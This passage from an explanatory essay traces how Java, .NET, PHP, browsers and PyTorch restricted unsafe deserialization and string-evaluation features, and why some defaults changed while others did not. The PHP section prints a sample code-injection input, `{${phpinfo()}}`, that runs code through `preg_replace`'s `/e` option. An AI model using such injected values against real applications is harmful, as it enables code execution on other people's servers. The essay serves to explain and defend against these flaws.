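The final `!*` is easy to forget. Without it, the filter returns "undecided" for every class outside the package, and Java builds the object. InfoQ's example of a "white-list" is a single package pattern with no `!*`, so on its own it would allow the whole Commons Collections chain.

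JEP 290 excludes defining "any specific policy of what classes should be allowed or disallowed". Each application's developers have to write their own, and Oracle's manual page *Java Serialization Filters* states that a filter "is not enabled or configured by default". If they do nothing, their program is as exposed as it was before the filter existed. In terms of the six stages, JEP 290 added a safer option alongside the unsafe call but did not change the default.

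Writing the policy is also hard. Sayar and colleagues examined ten vulnerable applications to see whether they could extract a list of needed classes from the code. All ten used general types such as "a list of any objects", so an allowlist based on the code would have had to contain every serializable class. The alternative is to ask the developers, who may have left or forgotten which classes are needed. Even a good list must be updated as the application changes. If the next version of `Order` contains one of Java's standard lists, the filter above will reject every order until somebody adds the missing class.

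A denylist breaks fewer programs but protects them less, because an attack can become possible even when the program itself hasn't changed. Kreyssig and colleagues searched 533 widely used libraries for "dormant" chains, which lack only a link or so. They made small changes that a maintainer might make innocently, such as marking a class as serializable, and ran three detection tools before and after. The tools reported new chains in 26% of the libraries, and the researchers manually confirmed dormant chains in 53 libraries. The missing link can also come from a different library, a combination that neither set of maintainers controls.

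New critical flaws in Java deserialization have kept appearing, and Kreyssig and colleagues counted 55 published between 2020 and early 2025. One, from 2024, was in part of Apache Lucene, a search library. When a server replied with an error, Lucene's client deserialized the reply to find out what had gone wrong, and built the object before checking that it was an error.

### An off switch that few people use

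A single filter for the whole process is too coarse, because one program may read both orders from strangers and its own saved data. JEP 415, proposed for Java 17 (Reinhold, 2021, *JEP proposed to target JDK 17*), lets a program install a "filter factory" that chooses a filter for each deserialization. According to OpenJDK's specification, it also added a way to reject classes that a filter leaves undecided, which closes the gap left by a missing `!*`. But programs have to opt in to the factory too. OpenJDK's *Implement Context-Specific Deserialization Filters (8u)*, written when developers were preparing the same feature for Java 8, states that use of filters on individual streams "is thought to be minimal". This was the developers' impression rather than a count, though they would be likely to hear complaints.

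While JEP 415 was under discussion, the developer Peter Firmstone called the filters a design mistake. Firmstone argued that they further complicated an already complicated game of Whack-a-Mole, and that the time would be better spent on a new serialization system and a switch to turn the old one off. Riggs (2021), in *New candidate JEP*, replied for Oracle that the switch already existed. Since Java 9, anyone could start a program with only the filter `!*`, which rejects all classes. Riggs added that Firmstone's proposal did nothing for "existing production apps dependent on serialization".

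Riggs was right that administrators could already turn the feature off, but this protected only those who knew they needed to. The Rails emergency had shown that many developers do not know which formats their software accepts.

### Waiting for Marshalling

At a conference in London in 2018, Oracle's chief Java architect, Mark Reinhold, called serialization "a horrible mistake in 1997" that some of the team had tried to stop. ADTmag's *Removing Serialization from Java Is a 'Long-Term Goal' at Oracle* (2018) reports his estimate that it had played a part in at least a third of all Java vulnerabilities, and possibly more than half. He thought its only attraction was that it was easy to use in simple cases. He wanted it removed but gave no date.

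*Towards Better Serialization* outlines a possible replacement. A programmer would mark one constructor, or a similar method, to rebuild an object and another method to take it apart. Every incoming value would pass through the class's own checks, so the range from 5 to 1 would fail as it does in ordinary code. The same two methods could be used to save objects as JSON, XML or bytes. Programmers could no longer save objects that contain each other in a loop, and each class would need its own code instead of inheriting the behaviour. The paper argues that nearly all users want to store data, not perfect copies of running objects, and that many of serialization's worst problems come from serving the remaining 0.1%.

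The note, which is explicitly exploratory, also includes a timetable for moving Java's own classes to the new serialized form. One release would add support for reading the new form, the next would start writing it, and a third would stop reading the old one. With a release every six months, this could take "as little as 18 months", according to the note.

Removing serialization has taken far longer, because its replacement has to exist first. In June 2025, Liang (2025), an Oracle engineer, wrote in *Explicitly mark JEP 154 / JDK-8046144 as April Fools joke* that Oracle plans "to resume the process of removing serialization once Marshalling is available". Marshalling is the replacement, and until it arrives, serialization would get mostly critical fixes. Liang was discussing JEP 154, "Remove Serialization", which is dated 1 April 2012, rates its impact on Twitter as "High", and is widely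 read as an April Fools' joke. Liang doubted that it was a joke, but the evidence that Oracle currently intends to remove serialization comes from Liang's and Reinhold's statements, not from JEP 154.

Marshalling was still unfinished in late 2026. Its developers have presented it at conferences since 2024. The description of a talk published in November 2025, Inside Java's *Serialization 2 0* (2025), promises a simpler and safer model that works with many data formats. In February 2026, Inside Java's *Java Serialization* (2026), from Oracle's Java team, still described work to "develop a replacement". The July proposals for Java 28 covered in InfoQ's *Java News Roundup* (2026) do not include Marshalling, although one new proposal that week would give Java a small built-in JSON library. The items the Java team posted on Inside Java (2026) from late October to 11 November include a talk on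 secure coding that covers serialization, but nothing on its replacement.

Oracle is also protecting serialization in a recent change that tightens the rules around it. Java programmers can mark a field as `final` so that it never changes after the object is created, but libraries have long been able to change such fields anyway, and many serializers depend on this. Foojay's *Finally final* (2026) explains that Java 26 prints a warning when a library changes a `final` field and that a later release will block the change by default. But code that rebuilds `Serializable` classes will still have a supported way around the rule. The developers of Tentackle, a Java framework with its own serializer, decided not to use this exception because it still bypasses constructors.

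### Microsoft switches BinaryFormatter off

BinaryFormatter arrived in 2002 with the first release of .NET Framework, Microsoft's platform for Windows programs. It had the same flaw as Java's serializer. DevClass' *Microsoft makes breaking change in .NET 9 for security* reports that Barry Dorrans, a security manager at Microsoft, admitted the class had led to remote code execution in the company's own Exchange, SharePoint and Azure DevOps.

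Microsoft had an unusual chance to start again. In 2016 it released .NET Core 1.0, a new version of the platform that also ran on Linux and macOS, and left BinaryFormatter out because of the known risks. Customers objected. In a discussion on GitHub, one wanted it for distributed systems, to send exceptions (the objects that describe an error) from one machine to another. Microsoft was already adapting other serializers to the new platform, but they could not handle exceptions as the old one had. According to Dorrans, somebody copied the code from .NET Framework and published it as a package, while large customers wrote to Microsoft's management that they could not move to the new platform without it. Microsoft put the class back in .NET Core 2.0. (Dorrans remembers it as version 1.1.)

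The second attempt began in 2020, when Microsoft published a plan to withdraw the class over several releases.

| Release | What happened to a program that used BinaryFormatter |
|---|---|
| .NET 5 (2020) | The compiler printed a warning. In web applications, the call failed with an exception unless the developer had turned it back on |
| .NET 7 (2022) | The compiler's warning became an error |
| .NET 8 (2023) | The call failed by default in most other kinds of program too |
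| .NET 9 (2024) | The call always fails, and the settings that used to turn it back on no longer exist |

Web applications came first, which makes sense because they are the most likely to read data from strangers. The setting that re-enabled the class was named `EnableUnsafeBinaryFormatterSerialization`, so anyone switching it on had to type the word "unsafe". The early notice also came from the compiler, whose output programmers have to read, rather than from a server log as with PyYAML. Microsoft's instructions explained how to silence the warning but recommended doing so only around a single call. However, an installed library that someone else had already compiled would produce no warning.

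### Reading a payload without executing it

Microsoft's migration guide recommends four replacements for BinaryFormatter. Two of them, a JSON serializer and an XML serializer called DataContractSerializer, come with .NET. DataContractSerializer is the easiest to adopt because it recognises the same markings on classes as BinaryFormatter. The other two, MessagePack and protobuf-net, are open source and store data in compact binary formats.

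New serializers do not help a company with ten years of files in the old format. For them Microsoft wrote NrbfDecoder, named after the format, .NET Remoting Binary Format. It reads the bytes and returns a description of what they contain, without building any of the objects they name. A program that needs to recover an old order can use it like this:

```
var record = (ClassRecord)NrbfDecoder.Decode(file);
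if (record.TypeNameMatches(typeof(Order)))
    order = new Order(record.GetString("customer"),
                      record.GetInt32("quantity"));
```

In the first line, the decoder produces a record with a type name, stored as text, and a set of named values. It does not look for a type to match the name. In the second line, the program compares the name with the one type it expects. If they match, the program passes a piece of text and a number from the record to the ordinary constructor, which applies all its checks. If the input is a gadget chain, the decoder returns records with unfamiliar names, the comparison fails, and the chain does not run.

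Microsoft compares this to using a JSON reader without a deserializer, and it does make the old format about as harmless as the JSON dictionary described earlier. It also has the same weakness if a developer looks up the type name and builds whatever it refers to. Developers have to write a few lines of code for every class. For old files, a developer could do this work once, by reading each file with the decoder and saving it in a new format.

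Microsoft took a similar approach with Windows Forms, its system for building desktop programs, which relied on BinaryFormatter for the clipboard and for stored images. A Windows Forms maintainer had warned in GitHub's *Epic- Update BinaryFormatter usage* that removing BinaryFormatter would "likely have far reaching impact". The team wrote a reader and writer that handle the old format for the most common types, such as text and images.

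### The package and the exemption

Developers who cannot switch can still restore BinaryFormatter by installing a separate package that Microsoft does not support and turning on the old "unsafe" setting. Microsoft describes the package as a stopgap and says it also brings back the vulnerabilities.

Only the application has to install the package. Every library it uses that calls BinaryFormatter then works again, unchanged. This helps when the call is in a library that nobody maintains, but a developer who installs the package for one library also re-enables the call in all the others. The opt-in is therefore much broader than Ruby's `unsafe_load`, which applies to a single line.

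One developer on GitHub, quoted by DevClass, predicted that companies would install the package, tell their security scanners to ignore it, and put off migrating more or less forever. The package is still in use. NuGet's *System.Runtime.Serialization.Formatters 11.0.0*, the package's page in the .NET catalogue, shows 309,442 downloads of that version in the few weeks after its release on 10 November 2026. Automated build systems download the same package repeatedly, so the number of programs using it could be far smaller. Microsoft is still publishing new versions of this stopgap two major releases after the removal.

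Microsoft's plan to retire BinaryFormatter exempted .NET Framework from the start. DevExpress' *Updates On Microsoft’s BinaryFormatter Obsoletion Strategy* (2023) quotes the plan as saying that BinaryFormatter would "continue to work as expected" there. The older platform is still widely used, and parts of it depend on BinaryFormatter. Microsoft also advises .NET Framework users to stop using BinaryFormatter, but has done nothing to force them to.

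Some users thought Microsoft had gone too far. One, commenting on its announcement, found it "really weird" to remove a whole feature instead of fixing a security issue, and complained that .NET now had no binary serializer of its own. Another reported that XML could turn a 1-kilobyte test file into more than 64 kilobytes, and was staying on .NET 3.5, a version of .NET Framework. A third had temporarily switched to JSON and expected to move to MessagePack because its files were much smaller.

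Microsoft replied that the problem was the design, which lets the data determine which types the program creates, and that there was no bug to fix. The team had considered some minor breaking changes and concluded that they could not make the design sound. Other projects' experience supports this. PyYAML's maintainers spent nearly two years repairing FullLoader and gave up, and Java's filter works only when each application's developers supply their own list of classes. The complaint about binary formats is harder to dismiss, since both compact replacements come from outside projects.

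### Why only one of them is gone

The obvious explanation is that .NET users had something to move to and Java users do not. Microsoft's two attempts to remove BinaryFormatter are good evidence for this. In 2016 the company had sole control of .NET and a separate old platform for customers who needed BinaryFormatter, but the removal failed, and Microsoft blames the lack of "a clear migration path". Microsoft still had both in 2024, but by then customers also had four recommended serializers, a decoder for old files, and a package for emergencies. They had also had four years of notice, which may explain part of the success.

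However, maintainers partly decide what counts as a replacement. None of Microsoft's four replacements does everything that BinaryFormatter did, but the company decided that they were good enough. For Java, *Towards Better Serialization* names more than forty alternative libraries, but says that most of them improve the format or the speed without solving the main problem, which is how to rebuild objects without bypassing their constructors. Marshalling should solve that problem, and every new serializer could then build on the result. But Oracle's higher standard has left the old default in place while the work continues.

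Microsoft could make many of the repairs itself because it maintained the compiler, the web framework and Windows Forms, and could change them all to fit the plan. Oracle controls less of the software that depends on Java serialization. Kreyssig and colleagues point out that Android apps still use it to communicate with one another, and Google owns Android. But Microsoft's ownership also meant that all the complaints went to one company, and in 2016 the emails from large customers helped bring BinaryFormatter back.

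Microsoft let customers who could not move to current .NET stay on .NET Framework, which still has the unsafe class. Java has no separate product of this kind. Oracle still patches old releases, including Java 8, but companies expect to be able to move their programs to the next release. Microsoft's success is also smaller than it looks, because it protects programs on current .NET but not those on .NET Framework, which are often the oldest.

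None of this explains why Oracle has not changed the default. Removing serialization may have to wait for Marshalling, but Oracle could already make Java refuse all classes unless a program supplies its own filter. The filter `!*`, available since Java 9, refuses all classes. This would be roughly the step Microsoft took in .NET 8. The drawback, which Riggs raised in 2021, is that a great many working programs would stop until somebody listed the classes they need.

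## Functions that run strings as code in PHP and JavaScript

PHP runs on web servers and JavaScript runs mostly in browsers. Both still have an `eval` function. PHP's developers removed several other features that ran strings as code less visibly. Browser makers could not remove `eval` from JavaScript without breaking existing pages, so they let each website switch it off for its own pages. Google imposed the restriction on all browser extensions.

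### PHP votes out its hidden evaluators

PHP's developers decide on changes through written proposals, called RFCs ("requests for comments"), and publish how each person voted. In one of these, Popov (2012), in *RFC*, proposed removing an option of `preg_replace`, a function that finds text matching a pattern and replaces it. If the programmer added the letter `e` after the pattern, PHP ran the replacement as code. This line puts bold text into capitals:

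```
preg_replace('/<b>(.*?)<\/b>/e', 'strtoupper("$1")', $text);
```

If the text contains `<b>hello</b>`, PHP copies "hello" into the place marked `$1`, runs `strtoupper("hello")` and gets "HELLO". But a visitor to the site might submit `<b>{${phpinfo()}}</b>`, in which case PHP runs this:

```
strtoupper("{${phpinfo()}}")
```

PHP evaluates expressions in braces inside a double-quoted string, so it calls `phpinfo`, which prints details of the server. An attacker could call a more harmful function. PHP added a backslash before any quotation mark in the copied text to stop visitors from ending the string early, but this attack contains no quotation marks. Popov argued that the backslashes gave programmers "a false feeling of security". They could also corrupt ordinary text, for example by leaving a stray backslash before an apostrophe in a heading.

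The replacement was a callback, an ordinary function that PHP calls for each match:

```
preg_replace_callback('/<b>(.*?)<\/b>/',
    function ($m) { return strtoupper($m[1]); }, $text);
```

Here the visitor's text reaches `strtoupper` as a value and never becomes part of the source code. The function returns the attack as harmless text, `{${PHPINFO()}}`.

One developer objected that unchecked input always causes trouble, and that removing `/e` would inconvenience many people for no real gain. Another answered that checking input properly was hard, and that people regularly got it wrong without knowing. Popov's own example supported this. It used double quotes where single quotes would have been safe, a mistake one participant thought even veterans would miss. Others suggested a setting to turn `/e` off. Popov expected shared hosting companies would never use it, for fear of breaking their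 customers' sites, although those customers needed the protection most.

The proposal passed by 23 votes to 4. PHP 5.5 began warning about `/e` in 2013, and PHP 7.0 removed it in 2015 after a second vote of 33 to 1, according to PHP's wiki. A nearly identical option in `mb_ereg_replace`, a similar function for text in other alphabets, had been overlooked. PHP deprecated that option about four years after the first vote, by 19 votes to 0, according to the later proposal on PHP's wiki.

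Popov (2015), in *PHP RFC*, then proposed deprecating two more hidden evaluators. The first, `create_function`, took a function's body as a string and passed it to `eval`. It dated from before PHP 5.3, when the language had no other way to write a small unnamed function within a program. Popov called it slow, wasteful of memory and a potential security problem. WordPress, the website software, had already removed most of its calls to `create_function`, and knutsp (2017), in *Remove (most) uses of create_function() from core*, pointed out that the coming warnings meant the last one would also have to be removed.

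The second was `assert`, which programmers use to check that a condition they expect to be true is true. If they gave it a string, PHP ran the string as code and checked the result. Before PHP 7, using a string was the only way to avoid evaluating a check when checks were turned off. But `assert($value)` looks like a harmless test of whether `$value` is filled in, and a visitor who could set `$value` to a string could run code. PHP's notes on version 7.2 give this risk as the reason for deprecating string arguments.

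The fourth case involved serialized objects rather than a string of source code. A Phar file, an archive that holds a PHP program, can include such objects as metadata. PHP rebuilt them whenever a program accessed the archive, even if the program only called `file_exists` to check for a file inside it. An attacker who could upload an archive and influence the path being checked could therefore trigger a gadget chain. In August 2018, korvinszanto (2018) asked PHP's developers to stop this behavior, citing remote code execution in the website system TYPO3. Since version 8.0, PHP has rebuilt the objects only when a program calls `getMetadata`.

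| Feature | Votes for and against | Deprecated | Removed | Replacement |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `/e` in `preg_replace` | 23–4 to deprecate, 33–1 to remove | PHP 5.5 (2013) | PHP 7.0 (2015) | A callback |
| `create_function` | 29–0 | PHP 7.2 (2017) | PHP 8.0 (2020) | An ordinary unnamed function |
| String arguments to `assert` | 25–1 | PHP 7.2 (2017) | PHP 8.0 (2020) | An ordinary condition |
| Automatic rebuilding of Phar metadata | 25–0 | No warning period | PHP 8.0 (2020) | An explicit call to `getMetadata` |

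The results of the two votes on version 7.2 come from the count Nikita Popov posted, and the result of the last vote comes from the proposal on PHP's wiki. PHP.Watch's *create_function* confirms the removal in 8.0.

The Phar change shows that a default can be easy to fix when few people rely on it. According to PHP.Watch's *PHP 8.0*, the change was unlikely to break any real application. TYPO3's developers had written their own guard against the attack, which ran on every request. Hader (2022), in *Drop typo3/phar-stream-wrapper due to improved handling in PHP*, removed it because PHP now provided the protection itself. Programs that request the metadata are still at risk, and PHP's *Phar::getMetadata* warns that the call can run arbitrary code if the archive comes from an untrusted source.

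These votes were lopsided largely because each feature had a replacement that worked at least as well. The same voters hesitate when the replacement is harder to adopt. In August 2025 they voted 18 to 9, exactly the two-thirds required, to deprecate `__sleep` and `__wakeup`, two methods that PHP calls when it saves and rebuilds an object. In the thread where Banyard announced the result, a developer of the Symfony framework objected that moving to the newer methods could require deep knowledge of PHP's storage format, because old and new versions of a program must still read each other's data. Grekas and Zelenka (2025), in *PHP RFC*, argued that the first proposal had understated how difficult the change would be, and PHP's developers reduced the deprecation to a note in the documentation.

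The same round of votes deprecated backticks, by 21 to 8. PHP runs any text between two backticks as a system command, exactly as its `shell_exec` function does. Programs can still run commands with `shell_exec`, which is much easier to spot in a review than a pair of backticks.

### Why eval itself stayed

Popov explained why PHP should remove `/e` but keep `eval`. A callback can replace every use of `/e`, but `eval` has a few uses with no sane alternative. It is also much easier to create a vulnerability by accident with `/e` than with `eval`. The PHP manual page for `eval` calls the feature "very dangerous" and discourages its use.

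Some administrators wanted to be able to turn `eval` off. PHP's `disable_functions` setting blocks functions by name, but it has no effect on `eval`, which is part of the language's grammar and not a function. spamik (2012), in *disable_functions = eval does not work*, reported this as a bug and later asked for `eval` to be off by default, because malicious programs use it to disguise their code. Popov replied that this would definitely not happen. In May 2019 the developers extended the setting to cover `eval`, but they reversed the change within three weeks at the request of the Xdebug debugger project. One developer then closed the request, arguing that no version of the switch could provide any security, since an attacker could save the same code to a file and load it. Another reopened it in February 2024, saying that one person should not make such a decision alone. It was still open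 in August 2026, and PHP's list of proposed deprecations for version 8.6 mentions neither `eval` nor `unserialize`.

In November 2019, Littman asked for the switch again, but with `eval` left on by default. Other developers objected, listing widely used packages that depend on `eval`, including the page-template system Twig and the testing tool PHPUnit. Littman had examples of malware that stopped working without `eval`, and argued that attackers should have to work a little harder. Critics answered that attackers would rewrite their tools, and that the switch would give site owners a false sense of security.

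The critics are mostly right about an attacker who can already run PHP on the server, which is the case both sides had in mind. A switch to turn off `eval` would do more against an attacker who can only send text to a program that carelessly passes it to `eval`. But a site that needs that call could not use the switch, so the benefit would be real but small, limited to sites with a forgotten call in a plugin they hardly use.

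### What allowed_classes protects against

PHP's deserializer, `unserialize`, has the familiar flaw that the data names the classes to build. PHP calls some of an object's methods automatically, for instance when it discards the object, and a gadget chain can start there. Since PHP 7.0, a programmer can restrict the classes:

```
unserialize($data, ["allowed_classes" => ["Order"]]);
```

If the data names any class other than `Order`, PHP produces a placeholder object that keeps the data but has none of the original class's methods. So a gadget chain made of other classes cannot run. Setting the option to `false` turns every object into a placeholder.

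If a programmer leaves the option out, `unserialize` still allows every class, as it did before. Like Java's serialization filter, the option offers more safety but leaves the default unchanged. According to the proposal on PHP's wiki, it also does not affect features that deserialize data without calling `unserialize`, such as session storage.

The proposal passed in 2014 by 17 votes to 6, a much closer result than the removals had. Malyshev, who proposed it, started a discussion on the developers' mailing list, where Popov opposed the option because it would encourage people to use `unserialize` on untrusted data without making that safe. The format lets one part of the data refer to another, so an attacker could build a structure that contains itself, the same problem that made Ruby's maintainers wary of YAML aliases. An attacker could also choose array keys that make PHP's tables extremely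 slow. Popov wanted an option that would let the developers tell users to forget all earlier warnings. Malyshev thought security was "a spectrum" and that it was worth giving some protection to programs that were going to use `unserialize` anyway.

The official advice is now closer to Popov's view. PHP's *unserialize* tells programmers not to pass it untrusted input, whatever the value of `allowed_classes`, and to use JSON instead. The proposal *improve unserialize error handling* says remote code execution is a danger "unless allowed_classes is configured to something safe". These statements are compatible because an attacker loses the gadget chain when the option is set to `false`, but may still be able to stall the server. If the option is set to a list of classes, safety also depends on what those classes' methods do.

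WordPress illustrates how slowly an optional protection spreads. Its function for reading stored data, `maybe_unserialize`, calls `unserialize` on behalf of plugins. In 2017, iandunn noted in *Add `allowed_classes` to `maybe_unserialize` When WordPress is running on PHP 7+* that most of those calls happen deep inside WordPress, where plugin authors cannot pass the new option. Eight years later, WordPress's *Adding Defense-in-Depth against PHP Object Injection* made a new proposal to refuse all classes by default and let plugins request exceptions.

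### JavaScript lets each site turn eval off

The owner of a PHP site chooses when to upgrade PHP and can test the site first. JavaScript on a web page runs in the visitor's browser, which upgrades itself, and the person who wrote the page may have abandoned it fifteen years ago. If a new browser version dropped `eval`, old pages would fail for visitors, who could only switch to another browser. *The Eval That Men Do* (Richards, Hammer and colleagues, 2011) recorded 550,358 calls to `eval` across more than 10,000 websites and found that at least half of the most popular sites used it. Many of the calls were unnecessary, but only the sites' own developers could rewrite them.

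Browser makers instead offered Content Security Policy, which major browsers have supported in its standard form since about 2013. Its main purpose is to limit cross-site scripting, an attack in which someone gets their own script to run inside another site's page, for example by posting it as a comment. The site's server sends a line like this along with the page:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self'
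```

The browser then loads script files only from the site's own address, ignores scripts written directly into the page, and raises an error when a script calls `eval` or a similar feature such as `new Function`. A site that needs `eval` can add the keyword `'unsafe-eval'` to the line. As with .NET's setting for BinaryFormatter, the developer has to type the word "unsafe", and the permission is broad. Every script on the page gets `eval`, even if only one chart library needs it. A site can also send the policy in a report-only form. The browser then blocks nothing but reports what it would have blocked, which gives the site's owner a runtime warning that visitors don't see.

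Few sites used the policy to block `eval` in 2022, about a decade after it became available. The HTTP Archive's *Web Almanac* for that year, based on a crawl of about eight million sites, found a policy on roughly 15% of them. Among policies with a `script-src` rule, about 80% included `'unsafe-eval'`. If the same proportion held for all policies, about 3% of sites blocked `eval`. The true share was probably lower, because many policies have no rule about scripts and only control, for example, whether other sites may display the page in a frame. The 2024 edition, which covered about 17 million sites, found a policy on about 19%.

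An older study suggests that many sites that tried to restrict scripts gained little. Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016), in *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, searched about 100 billion pages and found policies on 1.68 million hosts. On 99.34% of those hosts, the policy offered no benefit against cross-site scripting. Many sites allowed scripts written into the page. Others listed the outside addresses they trusted, but 14 of the 15 addresses most often listed for scripts also hosted something an attacker could use to bypass the policy. An allowlist of addresses thus has much the same weakness as an allowlist of classes, because a trusted entry may contain a gadget. The researchers, who worked at Google, recommended marking each approved script with a random code that changes every time the page loads.

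Trusted Types, a later addition to Content Security Policy, checks strings before the browser treats them as part of the page. Many cross-site scripting attacks succeed because a page's own code passes text from a visitor to a browser feature that interprets it as page content, such as `innerHTML`. If a site sends `require-trusted-types-for 'script'`, the browser refuses plain strings there, and also in `eval` if the site still permits it. The code must first pass the string through a function that the site's developers have registered, which can clean or reject it. Reviewers can then concentrate on a handful of these functions instead of every line that changes the page. However, a developer can still register a function that returns its input unchanged, which provides no protection.

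Chrome and Edge have supported Trusted Types since 2020. Safari followed in September 2025 and Firefox in February 2026, so for almost six years a site that adopted Trusted Types protected only some of its visitors. Each site still has to opt in.

### Extensions get no choice

A browser extension is a small program, such as a password manager, that a user adds to the browser. Many extensions can read and change every page the user visits, so a hijacked one can do more harm than a hijacked website. Each extension includes a file called a manifest, which lists the permissions its developer requests. Under version 2 of Chrome's manifest format, the browser blocked `eval` in an extension's own pages by default, but the developer could restore it with `'unsafe-eval'` and also load scripts from approved outside servers.

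Manifest V3, which Chrome began accepting in January 2021, removed both opt-ins. An extension must now contain all its code when the developer submits it to Google's store. Google requires this because its reviewers can inspect only what is in the package, and a developer, or someone who has taken over the developer's server, could change remotely hosted code after the review.

Extensions can still download data, such as a list of addresses to block. To keep developers from using this to get around the ban, the store's rules forbid building an interpreter that runs complex commands fetched as data. A browser cannot easily enforce this rule, because the download may be plain JSON and the interpreter ordinary code, so enforcement depends on reviewers noticing violations.

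Google still supports two ways for extensions to run strings as code, both narrower than `'unsafe-eval'` on a web page. An extension can call `eval` in a sandboxed page, which lacks the extension's special permissions, and those are most of what an attacker would want. Extensions whose whole purpose is to run scripts that users write or install themselves can use a dedicated interface, but only after the user, who bears the risk, turns on a separate switch in the browser.

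In 2025, Google disabled the remaining Manifest V2 extensions in Chrome, more than four years after it introduced the new format. Developers had to switch formats or lose their Chrome users. Google could enforce this because it runs both the browser and the extension store, and could turn off extensions that nobody maintained. No company has that power over web pages. A browser that blocked `eval` everywhere would break pages that still worked in competing browsers, so millions of site owners each decide whether to block it. An owner who never sends the policy that blocks `eval` sees no error and has no code to fix, and much of the harm from an attack falls on the site's visitors.

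## Model files in machine learning: pickle, PyTorch and safetensors

A trained machine-learning model consists mainly of a large set of numbers, called weights. Training is expensive, so many developers download weights that someone else has trained, usually from Hugging Face, the largest website for sharing models. The weights themselves contain no code, but PyTorch, the main library for building models, saves them with Python's pickle, so for years anyone who opened a stranger's model also ran whatever instructions the file contained.

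PyTorch's developers made a safe loader the default in January 2025. They had a short allowlist, gave six months of warnings and wrote an error message that explained what to do. Even so, the old setting is hard-coded in several libraries built on PyTorch, so people who load models through those libraries still get the unsafe loader.

### Inside a model file

PyTorch programmers usually save a state dict, a table that lists a model's weights by name. Each entry is a tensor, a grid of numbers. PyTorch's *Serialization semantics* gives the layout of the resulting file, which is a ZIP archive. Without a few details, it looks like this:

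```
model.pt
    data.pkl
    data/0
    data/1
    version
```

The numbered files contain the weights. `data.pkl` contains the pickle instructions for assembling them into a table, and an attacker would put malicious code there.

*PICKLEBALL* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) describes two instructions that matter for models, besides the `c` (import) and `R` (call) instructions from the "hello" example. `NEWOBJ` creates an object of an imported class without running its usual setup code, and `BUILD` fills in the object's attributes. Harmless model files need such instructions too, because PyTorch has to call a function to turn stored numbers back into a tensor. A security tool therefore can't reject every file that calls a function, and has to check which names the file imports.

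Model scanners do this with denylists. Kellas and colleagues tested two of them on 84 malicious models, including 82 that earlier studies had found on Hugging Face. ModelScan, which Hugging Face uses, missed nine, five of them because they called functions not on its list. The other missed 40. Hugging Face's own tool also marked parts of a popular, harmless text-processing model as suspicious.

### A loader that imports nothing

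In 2022 PyTorch's developers added a setting called `weights_only` to `torch.load`, the function that opens a model file. With `weights_only=True`, PyTorch uses its own version of pickle's stack machine, which follows the same instructions under stricter rules:

| Instruction | Ordinary pickle | `weights_only=True` |
|---|---|---|
| `c` (import) | Imports any module the file names and takes a function or class from it | Looks the name up in a fixed list and stops with an error if it is missing |
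| `R` (call) | Calls whatever function is on the pile | Calls only functions on the list |
| `NEWOBJ` (create) | Creates an object of any class | Creates objects only of classes on the list |
| `BUILD` (fill in) | Sets attributes on any object | Works only on tensors, a few related types and classes the user has added |

The first version of the list, in PyTorch's *Add `weights_only` option to `torch.load` (#86812)*, permitted only plain values such as numbers, text, lists and dictionaries, along with tensors and a few other PyTorch types. It did not permit `print` or `os.system`, so the loader would reject the "hello" stream at its first instruction. In later versions, a programmer who trusts another class can add it with `add_safe_globals`.

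The default changed in three steps:

| Release | What a plain call to `torch.load` does |
|---|---|
| 1.13 (2022) | Runs any code in the file, unless the programmer asks for `weights_only=True` |
| 2.4 (July 2024) | Still runs any code, but prints a warning that the default will change |
| 2.6 (January 2025) | Uses the restricted loader, unless the programmer asks for `weights_only=False` |

Kellas and colleagues date PyTorch 2.6 to November 2024. The new default was in PyTorch's nightly test builds late that year, but PyTorch (2025) announced the finished release on 29 January 2025.

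PyYAML's maintainers made the same change in 2018 and withdrew it two days later. In PyTorch, the change should have been painless for most users, because an ordinary state dict loads under either setting. Three kinds of file cause trouble: those that contain a whole model object instead of its weights, those with custom kinds of tensor, and those with values from NumPy, a common library for numerical work.

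The PyTorch developer mikaylagawarecki explained the need for the change in *BC-Breaking Change* by citing an attack at ByteDance, the company that owns TikTok. An intern had put code into checkpoints, the copies of a model that a program saves during training, and used them to attack training on a large cluster of machines. PyTorch's error message advises people to turn the restriction off only for files from a trusted source, but a colleague's checkpoint on the company's own machines would normally count as trusted. The attack therefore supports a safe default more than a warning about strangers' files, since a default also covers files that nobody thinks to distrust.

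### Flaws in the safe mode

In April 2025 PyTorch's maintainers disclosed that the safe mode could run an attacker's code. The GitHub Advisory Database's *PyTorch* (2025) credits Ji'an Zhou with finding the flaw, CVE-2025-32434. In OSV, another vulnerability database, *PyTorch* (2025) rates its severity 9.3 out of 10. The flaw affected versions 2.5.1 and earlier, and version 2.6 fixed it.

Anyone who had upgraded for the new default was therefore already protected when the flaw became public eleven weeks later. Careful users who had stayed on an older version were worse off. PyTorch's *Add warning for weights_only (#129239)*, the change behind the 2024 warning, recommended `weights_only=True` for any file the user did not fully control. In versions 2.4 and 2.5, a malicious file could still run code on the machines of people who followed this advice.

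Some users could not upgrade. In the forum thread *Fix to make torch.load safer in Pytorch v2.1.2*, one user described copying ten changes from 2.6 into 2.1.2 and getting test errors. The reply was that a backport made little sense for such an old version, and that the flaw "only matters if you load untrusted model from the wild". That is correct, but the setting was meant to make such files safer to load.

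PyTorch's developers have since made weaker claims about `weights_only=True`. The October 2025 revision of their *Serialization semantics* says the setting "narrows the surface" for attacks that run code. It adds that the setting does not stop files designed to stall a program, and that a file might still corrupt the program's memory.

Three months later, a second flaw showed that the last caveat was needed. According to the GitHub Advisory Database's *PyTorch Vulnerable to Remote Code Execution via Untrusted Checkpoint Files* (2026), Zhou found that the loader would follow an instruction to add dictionary entries to objects that were not dictionaries. It also did not check that a tensor's declared size matched the data in the file. An attacker could use these gaps to corrupt memory and possibly run code. Version 2.10 fixed them.

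The 2026 flaw in PyTorch was in how the loader itself handled data, which an allowlist of names does not check. PyTorch could fix it without changing what users are allowed to load, unlike the flaws in PyYAML's FullLoader, which depended on the classes and functions the loader allowed.

### Libraries that switch the safe loader off

Kellas and colleagues measured how many existing models the restricted loader would refuse. They examined the 1,500 most popular Hugging Face repositories (project folders) that offered models only as pickle files, and could trace the contents of 1,426. In 219 of these, or 15.4%, at least one model used a function or class outside the loader's default list. People downloaded those 219 repositories 79.6 million times in one month.

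Only 36 distinct names caused all the refusals, and many came from major libraries such as NumPy. PyTorch's developers could check these by hand, but each name they allowed would give attackers another part for a gadget chain.

Many refused files are harmless. In September 2024, the developer njzjz tried to move a project to the safe setting in *fix(pt): set weights_only=True for torch.load*, but loading failed. The program had saved the learning rate, which controls how fast a model trains, as a NumPy number instead of an ordinary Python one.

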